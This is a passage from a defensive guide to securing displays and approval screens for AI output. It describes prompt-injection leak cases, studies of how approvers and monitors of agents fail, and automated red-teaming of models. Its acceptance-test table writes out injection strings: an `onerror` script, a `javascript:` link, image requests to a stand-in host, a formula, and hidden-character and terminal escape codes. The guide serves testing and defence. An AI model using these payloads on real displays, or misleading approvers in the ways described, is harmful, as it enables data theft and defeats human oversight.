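The queue already shows web addresses as text, and it should do the same with telephone numbers and email addresses. Some phones automatically turn anything that looks like a telephone number into a link, but a page can switch this off on iPhones with the `format-detection` setting. Blocking outside images removes QR codes like Permiso's, but someone can also draw a QR code with Unicode's solid block characters. The tool can replace long runs of those characters with a count.

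None of this stops a reviewer from dialling a number by hand. The marketplace also needs a rule that staff take contact details from the customer's record or the staff directory, never from an AI's answer. Looking up a customer's number before ringing back takes an agent a few seconds, and a false number in the chat then does no harm.

The tool can support that rule with an alert. Figueroa recommends scanning summaries for telephone numbers, web addresses and urgent security language, and flagging or removing what the scan finds. A review tool should flag these items but not remove them, because they are evidence. An alert such as "This telephone number is not in the staff directory" gives the reviewer a fact they can check at once, which fits HAT-Lab's finding about easy checks. An attacker can avoid the scan by spelling out the number or asking the reader to reply in the chat.

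The flagged-answer queue should reserve interruptions for such cases, because reviewers would soon dismiss a dialog that appeared on every answer.

### Opening the source

A reviewer who doubts a sentence should be able to open the matching passage beside the answer with one click and see a few lines of context. The tool must show the text that the model received. If it showed the email from the Gemini case as Gmail displays it, the reviewer would see blank space where the planted instruction was, and might conclude that the warning came from Google. The plain text would show the instruction, but it needs the same protections as the answer, including the boundary and visible codes for hidden characters, because an outsider wrote it.

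The tool should show the original figure next to the model's version so that a corrupted number is easy to spot. In HAT-Lab's travel task, a column of fares from the companies' own systems would have revealed the extra ten dollars without any searching.

Reviewers can't catch some false statements by opening the source. If a seller falsely describes a product as safe for infants, an accurate summary will repeat the claim and match the source. The label "outside seller" shows the reviewer whose claim it is, but the reviewer needs evidence from someone else to check it.

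## Building approval screens from the action itself

A false sentence can do more damage on an approval screen, because the software acts as soon as the reviewer accepts it. Suppose the marketplace lets an AI agent propose refunds, and staff must approve each one. If the agent writes the description on the screen, such as "Refund 40 euros for a damaged lamp", the reviewer approves that sentence, but the software carries out the underlying payment request, which may be different. Researchers have shown that an attacker can make such descriptions misleading.

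In June, Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, proposed a remedy called consent integrity. It requires a separate component, outside the agent's control, that does four things:

1. It intercepts the real action and builds the screen from that, not from the agent's description.
2. It shows every effect that matters for security, such as deleting data or contacting an outside server.
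3. It displays the screen and collects the answer somewhere the agent can't draw over the text or answer for the reviewer.
4. It permits only the exact action that the reviewer approved.

No program can work out the effects of every action, so Weng sets a more modest goal for real systems. If the component can't tell what an action would do, it marks the action "uninspectable" and asks the reviewer, instead of letting it through as safe.

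For the fourth requirement, the component can use a hash, a short code that changes if the data it is calculated from changes. It calculates one hash from the complete action when it displays the screen and another just before the action runs, and refuses the action if they differ. It could also store the action and run only the stored copy. Each approval should expire and work only once, or the agent could repeat an approved payment.

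### What you see is what you sign

The idea comes from digital signatures, which prove that the holder of a secret key approved particular data. A compromised computer could display one contract and sign another, so security researchers required that "what you see is what you sign". Hardware wallets, small devices that hold the keys to cryptocurrency, meet this requirement with their own screen. The device's secure chip sends the amount and destination straight to that screen, where the computer can't alter them.

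European payment rules apply the same principle. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) explains that the code that approves a remote payment must be valid only for the amount and payee that the payer saw.

Weng points out that agents are harder for two reasons. An attacker may have compromised the program that would normally write the summary, and the real action may be hard to read. A payment consists of a few meaningful fields, but the command `python3 deploy.py` reveals almost nothing about its effects, which depend on what is in `deploy.py`. Weng's prototype therefore reads that file too.

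### A payment

The marketplace's refund screen could look like this:

```
PAY      40.00 euros
TO       account 7731 (customer 2048)
CHECK    same account that paid for order 5512
FROM     marketplace refunds account

[Refuse]   [Approve this payment]

Written by the AI agent, not checked   [show]
```

The amount and both account numbers come from the pending payment request. The customer number and the comparison with the original payment come from the marketplace's records. The agent supplies none of these fields, and its explanation stays hidden until the reviewer opens it.

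The screen identifies the payee by account because names can be ambiguous. Kodathala and colleagues found this problem in a sample screen for AP2, Google's protocol for payments by agents. That sample screen showed a name the merchant had chosen, but the approval covered the merchant's ID, so two merchants could look identical to the person approving. The signed approval itself withstood their tests.

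### An email

| What the reviewer needs to see | Where the system gets it |
|---|---|
| Every recipient, including blind copies | The message waiting to go out |
| The subject and full text | The message waiting to go out |
| Each attachment, and what the agent made it from | The file and a log of the agent's earlier steps |
| Whether a recipient is new | The company's past email |
| Any limits the user set | The user's original request, word for word |

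The agent probably wrote the email's subject and text, but they are part of the action, so the screen has to show them in full. They need the same protections as any other model output, including a fixed boundary, links shown as text and visible codes for hidden characters. The agent's reasons for sending the email are separate and belong in the closed box.

Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 language models to decide whether to approve an email whose description left out one recipient. All 15 approved the email when they saw only the description and refused it when the screen listed every recipient.

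An approval screen can list an action's fields accurately and still not reveal a problem. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. The agent later asks to send `report.csv` to the auditor. The recipient and file name look fine, but several steps earlier the agent had copied individual invoices into the file. The reviewer can catch this only if the screen shows both the user's restriction and where the attachment's contents came from.

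### A code change

Suppose a coding agent wants to send its changes to a repository, a shared store of a project's code. The screen should show:

- **The destination**, and whether the public can read it. The service that hosts the repository supplies both.
- **The changed lines.** The version-control program calculates these by comparing the old and new files.
- **The change's identifier.** In Git this is a hash, so editing even one line after approval produces a new identifier, which the approval doesn't cover.
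- **Any scripts that will run**, with their contents.
- **Any unsaved work that the command would destroy.**

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes giving an automated checker two of these facts, whether the destination is public or private and the state of unsaved work. A human reviewer needs them too. For example, a push that is routine when it goes to a team's private repository can be a leak when it goes to a public one.

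The agent's code comments and commit message will become part of the repository, so they should appear with the changed lines, marked as the agent's text. A claim such as "this only fixes the login page" goes in the closed box.

### Whether to show the agent's explanation at all

Weng allows the approval screen to show the agent's explanation if a label marks it as untrusted. Kodathala and colleagues tested whether that is safe, using simulated approvers and 609 attack scenarios in which the agent lied about its action. One simulated approver, which perfectly compared the displayed action with the user's task, let through 54% of attacks when it saw only the agent's description and 3% when it saw a screen built from the real action. Another approver believed the agent's explanation whenever it was visible. It let through 54% with either screen, and 5% once the researchers removed the explanation.

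The 15 language models behaved differently. When they saw the real action, removing the explanation changed at most two of any model's 34 decisions. Nobody knows which pattern people would follow. Putting the explanation in a closed box is a reasonable compromise for most actions, but a payment screen has so few fields that it can omit the explanation.

### Weng's tests on commands

Weng tested the prototype on commands from two public collections. GTFOBins, which lists ways to misuse ordinary Unix programs, supplied 1,330 commands, and tldr-pages supplied 28,798 examples of normal use. The percentages for ordinary commands are Weng's, and the counts and the 8.9% are calculated from them.

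| Result | Documented abuses | Ordinary commands |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt that named a danger | 405 (30.5%) | about 2,563 (8.9%) |
| Prompt marked "uninspectable" | 792 (59.5%) | about 25,054 (87.0%) |
| No prompt | 133 (10.0%) | about 1,181 (4.1%) |

The prototype caught 90% of the abuses, but mostly by labeling them as commands it couldn't inspect. It applied that label even more often to ordinary commands, so the label is almost useless for judging whether a command is dangerous. A warning that names a danger is more useful, since it appeared about 3.4 times as often on abuses as on ordinary commands.

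The 133 abuses that passed silently varied in seriousness. Weng counts 85 that wrote to temporary folders, 19 that wrote project files which would do harm only if a later step used them, and eight basic operations such as creating a folder. The other 21 exposed real gaps in the analysis. An earlier version of the prototype missed 15.0% of abuses. Weng measured the improvement to 10.0% on the same collection, so the prototype may miss a larger share elsewhere.

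The prototype also exposed all 22 malicious actions in a smaller set that Weng wrote. Weng gives this result little weight because an earlier version also scored perfectly on its own test cases but missed common abuses.

These tests cover only part of the design. Weng built the analysis, the display text and the hash check, but only assumed complete interception and a protected display. If an agent acts by a route that the component doesn't intercept, the reviewer never sees a screen for that action. The tests used a stand-in for a commercial agent. They also involved no people, so they can't show whether a reviewer would understand an accurate screen.

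### Missed dangers and too many prompts

The prototype has a list of trusted tools, whose commands run without a prompt if the prototype detects no danger in them. All 133 silent abuses used tools on that list. Removing tools from the list would catch more abuses but interrupt more ordinary work. Weng concludes that any component that examines only the command faces this trade-off, however it is tuned. Watching what a program does as it runs might help.

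Too many prompts also make reviewers miss dangers. Anthropic hired 1,053 testers for a coding task and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, with the rate falling from about 17% early in a session to 5% after 50 or more prompts. The prompt showed the dangerous command itself, so an accurate screen was not enough to stop most testers from approving it. The testers were not working on their own code, which may have made them less careful.

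Anthropic's AI checker blocked 89% of the same commands, and the company has made it the default for many users. But Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, found that such checkers can leave users with little control. Most of the five commercial agents they examined in May and June either asked for permission frequently or relied on an AI reviewer that users could barely see or adjust. Claude's chatbot once created an email draft without asking, although the user had set that tool to "Needs approval".

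Another approach is to reuse an approval within limits. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) tested a system called ConLeash that asks again only when an action goes beyond what the user has already allowed. In a study with 16 people, 41.9% of the agent's tool calls went ahead without a new prompt.

The trade-off should be much milder for the marketplace than for a coding agent. Weng's ordinary commands came from 6,503 tools, most of which the prototype didn't recognise. A support agent might need only refunds, emails and account changes, and the marketplace can define every field for these actions in advance. Kodathala and colleagues did this for the tools in their tests, and 97 harmless tasks needed an average of 0.75 prompts each.

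### Later versions that work

In *The Verifiable Action Card*, Irshad, Mughees and colleagues (2026) built the idea into a web browser with an AI agent. They note that Weng had assumed a protected display was available. They put theirs in the browser's own interface, where a web page can't change it. Before the agent submits a form, the browser reads the recipient, amount and destination from the form itself. It checks the recipient and amount again as it sends the request.

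Attacks succeeded in 78% of trials with no approval step, 72% with an ordinary confirmation and 0% with the new screen. The reviewer was a program that refused everything the screen marked as high-risk, so the 0% shows that the browser marked the attacks correctly, but not whether people would refuse them. The screen also doesn't appear when the agent only opens a web address, even though doing so can leak data.

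Kodathala and colleagues put their component on a separate server, which stores the agent's request and sends a screen to the user's phone. The phone signs a hash of the request, and the server runs only the stored copy. In their tests, a protected confirmation on the agent's own computer worked about as well as the phone, but no test involved an attacker who controlled that computer's display. The design doesn't solve the problem of repeated requests. Even with limits on how often the agent could ask, a simulated reviewer eventually approved a harmful action in 45–60% of trials.

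With this screen, the 15 language models caught 98% of attacks, up from 30% with the agent's description. They also refused 16% of harmless requests, but that rate would have been about 2% without the refusals caused by placeholder text in the test messages.

Many released tools still don't tie an approval to one exact action. Kodathala and colleagues could measure this for eight approval mechanisms in popular software for building agents. In four, the action could change after a person approved it. They rated the approval design in Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit as the strongest outside design they tested. The toolkit's hash covers the whole action, so the toolkit refuses an action that changed after approval.

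A tool can also apply the right check in only one place. TYPO3's *ADR-132* (2026), an open-source project's design decision record, reports that the software compared the approved action with the reviewed one on only one of its screens. The software could also carry out a destructive action without recording who had approved it. An audit should therefore test every route to approval and confirm that the action stops if the software can't save the record. IETF's *EP Authorization Receipts* (2026), an early draft, proposes giving each approval a signed receipt that outsiders could check.

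### A test with people

Hossain and colleagues tested four approval screens with 80 volunteers, 20 for each screen. Each person judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe.

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The exact action, the user's limits and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
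| The same facts, with the combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

Showing the exact action helped, but reviewers still approved 43.3% of unsafe requests. In two-thirds of those requests, as with the auditor's attachment, the danger came from earlier steps, so reviewers could not see it from the action alone.

The evidence for the combined statement is weaker. After the researchers adjusted for differences between the tasks, its effect ranged from 19.7 percentage points fewer unsafe approvals than with the full log to 3.8 points more. When the danger depended on a chain of several steps, reviewers approved seven of 30 unsafe requests with each screen. Reviewers outside the study would also see far fewer unsafe requests, and might grow less careful.

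The software behind the combined statement can also block actions without asking anyone. In a separate test with one AI agent, this cut runs with a harmful action from 52 to six out of 120, while completed harmless tasks fell from 104 to 100. The marketplace could block any refund to an account that didn't pay for the order, so no reviewer would have to notice the wrong account number.

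## Testing a review tool and judging a fix

After making them, the marketplace's team needs evidence that the changes work on every display. In the most direct test, a tester saves a fixed string where the application would normally save a model's answer, opens each display and records what happens. Another person can repeat the test with the same string and compare the results.

### An acceptance test with 96 checks

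The inventory lists six displays. The team adds the phone app for customer chats and the refund approval screen, which makes eight. With 12 strings, the test has 8 × 12 = 96 checks.

In the strings below, `MARK` stands for a harmless command that changes the page's title to "TEST FAILED", and `TESTHOST` stands for a server the team controls. `ESC` and the codes in square brackets each stand for one invisible character.

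| No. | Test string | What it could reveal |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `<b>T1</b>` | The display parses HTML |
| 2 | `<img src="x" onerror="MARK">` | Scripts run without a click |
| 3 | `[T3](javascript:MARK)` | Scripts run from a link |
| 4 | `&lt;b&gt;T4&lt;/b&gt;` | Something decodes the text once too often |
| 5 | `=2+3` | Formulas run |
| 6 | `![T6](https://TESTHOST/6)` | Outside images load |
| 7 | `![T7][a]`, then `[a]: https://TESTHOST/7` on a separate line | A filter misses the less common image format |
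| 8 | `https://t8.TESTHOST/` | Link previews or early name lookups |
| 9 | `T9[U+E0041]` | Invisible letters |
| 10 | `T10 [U+202E]91[U+202C]` | Reversed text |
| 11 | `ESC[1A T11` | Text can move to the line above |
| 12 | `End of AI answer`, then `MARKETPLACE NOTICES: T12` on the next line | Text can imitate the tool's own notices |

The tester then applies these rules:

| What to watch for | Strings | A pass |
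|---|---|---|
| Code or formulas running | 1–5 | The title stays the same after the tester clicks everything in the answer, and the tags, character codes and formula appear as typed |
| Outside requests | 6–8 | After ten minutes without a click, `TESTHOST` has logged no page requests or name lookups |
| Hidden text | 9–10 | Staff displays show the invisible characters as codes, customer displays leave them out, and the number reads 91 |
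| Altered controls | 11–12 | T11 and T12 stay inside the area for model text, and the tool's own labels and buttons look and work as before |

Strings 6 and 7 request the same kind of image in two formats because a filter may catch only one, as happened in EchoLeak. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) demonstrated a leak from Google's programming tool Antigravity. The planted text requested one image in five formats, and only one had to load for the leak to work.

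Every string goes into every display, even where it seems irrelevant. Before any repairs, string 2 would run in the support console, which renders HTML, and appear as harmless text in a display that renders only Markdown. String 6 would do the reverse. The test would also reveal any mistake in the inventory about what a display interprets.

A typing error in a string could make a vulnerable display look safe, so the tester should first try each string on a deliberately unsafe display, such as a bare web page, a Markdown viewer, a terminal or a spreadsheet, and confirm that it works. The tester should also open `TESTHOST` by hand and check that the visit appears in its log.

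A few displays need extra steps. In the two chat displays, a stand-in for the model should send each string a few characters at a time, because some protections start only when an answer is complete. On the refund screen, the tester should put the strings in the agent's explanation. The tester should also run a test there that isn't among the 96, changing the amount after a colleague approves the refund and confirming that the payment stops.

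If the browser's Content Security Policy blocks an image, the display passes the test, but the tester should record the block. The block means the Markdown parser let the image through, leaving the policy as the only defence.

For each check, the tester records the date, the tool and browser versions, and a screenshot. At two minutes each, the 96 checks take 192 minutes by hand, though a script can run most of the browser checks much faster. A tool that passes 95 of them still leaves an attacker one way in, so the report should name the failure instead of giving a score of 99%.

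### What a test through the model measures

Many security tests send prompts to a live model and check its replies for dangerous text. They estimate how often the model produces such text, which helps people choose a model or judge how urgent a repair is, but they don't show how a display would handle the text.

For example, Mindgard's *AnsiEscaped*, an automated test for terminal codes, prompts a model to repeat a string that would make text blink. In Mindgard's example, the model repeats it with the escape character spelled out as `\u001b`, which is harmless unless another program decodes it. The test therefore detects a risk that depends on software outside the test. Mindgard's list of remedies includes preprocessing the input and adding guardrails, but not neutralising the codes when the text is displayed.

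A clean result from a model also leaves more room for failure than it may seem to. Suppose the team gives its assistant 300 documents with planted instructions, and the assistant never writes the image they ask for. If the true failure rate were 1%, the chance of 300 clean trials would be:

0.99³⁰⁰ ≈ 0.049

A model that fails 1% of the time would pass this 300-trial test about once in 20 attempts. A pass therefore lets the team rule out failure rates above about 1% at the usual 95% confidence, but not lower ones. When no trial fails, the upper limit is roughly 3 divided by the number of trials, so ruling out a rate above 0.1% takes about 3,000 clean trials. If the rate were 1%, a seller who planted the text in 300 product descriptions would have a 95% chance of at least one success.

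This calculation assumes that the trials are independent and that each has the same chance of failure. Running one prompt 300 times can meet these assumptions only for that prompt, and gives little evidence about other wordings. Trials that share a conversation aren't independent, because earlier replies affect later ones.

Attackers learn from each attempt and change their wording, so the failure rate of the first wording is a poor guide to that of the last. While testing the bank's assistant, Positive Security found that more complicated payloads came back encoded more often, and kept adjusting the text until the reply contained live HTML. Cisco, quoted by The Hacker News, criticises tests that send a model only one message, because real attackers rephrase refused requests, split up tasks and escalate gradually. Someone who can only plant documents gets less feedback than someone in a conversation,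 but can still learn which wording worked from a request in their server's log.

Willison argues that "99% is a failing grade" in application security. If 1% of attacks get through, an attacker will look for one that does. He was objecting to an *Economist* article which argued that AI developers should accept unreliable parts and add spare capacity, as Victorian engineers did with poor iron. That approach works for a bridge because nobody is searching for its weakest beam. Layers of defence still help a review tool, but at least one of them should stop the attack however the attacker words it.

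### Automated tools that search for failures

garak is an open-source tool from the chipmaker NVIDIA that tests language models. Its probes send a model prompts designed to provoke a particular kind of bad output, and its detectors check the replies for that output. A team can use it to compare models, or to repeat the same tests after a supplier updates one.

Fixed prompts become less useful as developers train models to resist them. Padmakumar, Derczynski and colleagues (2026), in *Training a General Purpose Automated Red Teaming Model*, trained a small model, Qwen3-8B, to write new attacks from a plain description of the goal. Their examples of goals that ordinary content-safety checks can miss include terminal codes and leaking data through a web address. The training worked as follows:

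1. A larger model read the goal and wrote specific examples of it, ways to disguise the request, and a scoring guide.
2. Qwen3-8B used the examples and disguises to write an attack.
3. A target model replied to the attack, and a judging model scored the reply with the guide.
4. Qwen3-8B received a reward of 1 for a successful attack, 0 for an unsuccessful one and −0.2 for an attack in the wrong format.

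The best version succeeded in 85% of attempts on goals used in training, up from 34% before training. On goals it had not seen, the success rate, measured with garak's detectors, rose from 21% to 29%. The tests targeted only two small models, so the rates are weak evidence about the large models in most products. The method matters more to a review tool's owner than these rates, because it can produce attacks for a new kind of output as soon as someone can describe that output.

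Most of the detectors search for fixed patterns, so they can miss an attack that reaches the goal in an unexpected way or count an unusually worded refusal as a success. For some goals, the success rate was zero both before and after training. Padmakumar and colleagues traced this to their own preparation, which had changed the goals so much that the attacks no longer aimed at what the detectors looked for. A team that saw only the zeros could have concluded that the target was safe.

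In early experiments, the researchers used a garak detector to set the reward. The attacks became simpler, and more of them earned the reward by exploiting the detector. A company that adjusted its product until garak found nothing could have a similar problem.

The marketplace can use these tools to extend its fixed test. If garak provokes a kind of output that the 12 strings don't cover, the team saves a harmless version of it as string 13, which adds eight checks. The display tests then cover that kind of output whether or not the next model produces it.

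### Judging a repair

A supplier that says an attack "no longer works" may have fixed the display, or may only have trained the model to refuse the published prompt. The buyer can find out which by putting the dangerous output, with a harmless placeholder, directly into the display. If the supplier doesn't allow that, the buyer can ask the model to repeat a test string exactly. If the model refuses, the test is inconclusive because the display never received the string.

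The retest should cover more than the screen in the original report:

- **Stored output.** The tester opens answers that the application saved before the repair. If the repair encodes each new answer as the application saves it, older answers may still contain live tags.
- **Other displays.** A repair to the customer's chat window may not reach the support console or the flagged-answer queue.
- **Mobile versions.** The tester checks each app separately, since OpenAI's first check on image addresses covered only the web version of ChatGPT.
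- **Exports.** The tester opens spreadsheets, emails and downloaded files in the programs that staff actually use.

A quick retest can leave much of a repair unchecked. Positive Security retested the bank's repair 41 minutes after the bank announced it. The retest gave good evidence about the customer's chat window but didn't cover the support agent's screen.

Flaws can also come from someone else's code. Google built Antigravity on code licensed from Windsurf, another programming tool. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* reports that Johann Rehberger had told Windsurf in May 2025 about a leak through Markdown images. When Google released Antigravity that November, Rehberger reproduced the leak there. A team that buys or copies a display should therefore look up old reports of flaws in the original product.

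The team should repeat all 96 checks whenever someone changes how a display renders text, including updates to a Markdown library or sanitiser. Risky changes can look like routine improvements. In April 2026, the contributor roroghost17 (2026) proposed that a log viewer show images attached to messages instead of hard-to-inspect raw data. The change used an ordinary image tag. With this change, opening the log could contact an outside server if an attached image's address pointed to one, although this is not a reported flaw. Strings 6 and 7 wouldn't catch this because they test Markdown in the message text. The team would need a new string in the attachment format.

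### Whether a leak counts as a vulnerability

Researchers and companies often agree on what a display did but not on whether that was a flaw. The table compares five reports and gives the latest public evidence on each.

| Report | First response | Later response | Latest public status |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's log viewer | Bugcrowd closed it as not applicable | OpenAI confirmed the flaw after publication | Repair under way on January 22, 2026, with no announced completion |
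| The bank's assistant | The bank said customers could attack only themselves | The bank accepted the report after clarification | Repaired on July 15, 2026, with the support agent's screen untested |
| ChatGPhish | Not reproducible | Not applicable, then duplicate | No announced repair as of publication on May 29, 2026 |
| Microsoft Copilot Chat | Microsoft investigated | Microsoft decided it was not a vulnerability | Closed without a repair on November 4, 2025 |
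| Images in Google Antigravity | Intended behaviour | Google listed it as a known issue and said it was working on repairs | Researchers demonstrated the leak again on June 17, 2026 |

Companies sometimes repair displays without announcing it, so a buyer should test the current version before relying on any of these entries.

Some of the early rejections came from confusion about the attack. For example, the bank changed its mind after the researchers explained how an outsider could plant the text. PromptArmor had given step-by-step instructions for the log viewer attack and answered questions on three separate days before Bugcrowd closed its report. It acknowledged that such reports are hard to fit into existing categories.

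OpenAI had some reason to reject the first ChatGPhish report. According to Permiso, OpenAI could not reproduce the behaviour from the details supplied. The report's title also claimed cross-site scripting, which Permiso's published demonstrations don't show. Permiso sent a fuller version the next day, without that claim in the title. "Duplicate" means OpenAI had already received a report of the same problem, so it doesn't imply the problem was harmless.

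The two companies may also have had different harms in mind. In January, OpenAI had said that it defends against attacks that leak data through web addresses. But the images in ChatGPhish had fixed addresses that carried no text from the conversation. They revealed the reader's network address, browser type and the time of the answer, and the false notices didn't require a leak. A check that stops private text from leaving in an address could therefore work perfectly and still allow this attack.

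Microsoft gave fuller reasons for its decision on Copilot Chat. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes how planted text made the assistant leak a secret key from a developer's environment through an image. Microsoft replied that the attack needed several actions that users don't take by default, did not work reliably in every environment, and came with warnings. Microsoft also assumes that people at work review and trust the code they run. It still passed the report to its engineers to look for ways to make the behaviour clearer to users.

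Checkmarx accepts that getting the assistant to read the planted text can be difficult, but argues that once it does, the image loads without any further action, and that Microsoft could have removed images or added a strict CSP. This argument is persuasive about the display. Difficult earlier steps make an attack less likely, but they don't justify leaving the last step open when ordinary code can close it.

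Checkmarx reported a related leak in Gemini. Gemini already blocked outside images, so this leak relied on the user clicking a link that carried private data. Google removes links to sites it knows to be malicious, but an attacker can register a new site. Google called the leak infeasible to fix and judged the risk too low to track as a security bug. Checkmarx called the answer acceptable, provided that Google warned users. A public chatbot would lose much of its value without links, so "infeasible" is a fair description in that case. Infeasibility is a poor reason to keep loading outside images in Antigravity, because Google had already turned them off in Gemini.

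The phrase "intended behaviour" makes Google's position on Antigravity sound more dismissive than it was. According to a Hacker News discussion copied on Brian Lovin's website, Google told researchers on its known-issues page that such reports would not earn a reward because it was already working on repairs. A company can reject a report under its reward rules and still accept that the flaw exists. CyberScoop reports that Google patched a separate Antigravity flaw in 2026 that let attackers run code.

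Google also warned users about data leaks when they first opened Antigravity. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* argues that the warning leaves too much to users. They can run several agents in the background, and the recommended settings let the agent decide when to ask for a review. PromptArmor considered it "extremely implausible" that users would check every action and keep sensitive data away from the tool.

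The June demonstration supports PromptArmor's argument. Antigravity prompted the user to approve a "visual debug token" without showing the command or the outside address, and the user agreed. But the user had also told the agent to follow instructions on an unfamiliar website, which fits the companies' point that some attacks depend on careless use.

Other companies also tell users to avoid untrusted content. Willison describes an attack on Cursor, another programming tool, that began with an email to a support desk. Software turned the email into a ticket, which a developer's agent read. Cursor called this a known issue and advised users to connect only to sources with trusted content. Willison replied that this advice won't work because attackers have too many ways to get text in front of a model. The marketplace couldn't follow it, since its assistant has to read sellers' descriptions.

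By contrast, Superhuman treated its leak through Google Forms as urgent, which Willison praised. A buyer can learn more from a supplier's reasoning and repairs than from the label on a closed report. A supplier is being honest if it says its model may still follow planted text, since no supplier has solved that problem. If it uses this to justify a display that loads whatever the model writes, the buyer should ask it to change the display.

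### A checklist for buyers and auditors

The best evidence is a trial account in which the buyer can run the 12 strings. If the supplier refuses, the buyer can ask for these records:

| What to check | Evidence to request |
|---|---|
| The supplier knows every display | A dated inventory that covers apps, exports, notifications and outside log viewers |
| Displays treat output as text | The exact test strings, software versions and screenshots, including any failures and the results from the deliberately unsafe displays |
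| Displays don't contact outside servers | The CSP that the live site sends, and the test server's log |
| Hidden characters can't mislead staff | Screenshots of strings 9 to 11 beside the stored bytes |
| Approvals cover one exact action | A recording in which someone changes an approved action and the system refuses it |
| Claims about the model are sound | The model's version, the number of trials, the different wordings used, and whether testers adapted them after failures |
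| Past repairs are complete | The original report, the reason for its classification, and retests of stored output, other displays, mobile versions and exports |
| Later changes don't undo repairs | Test results from the last three releases that changed a display |
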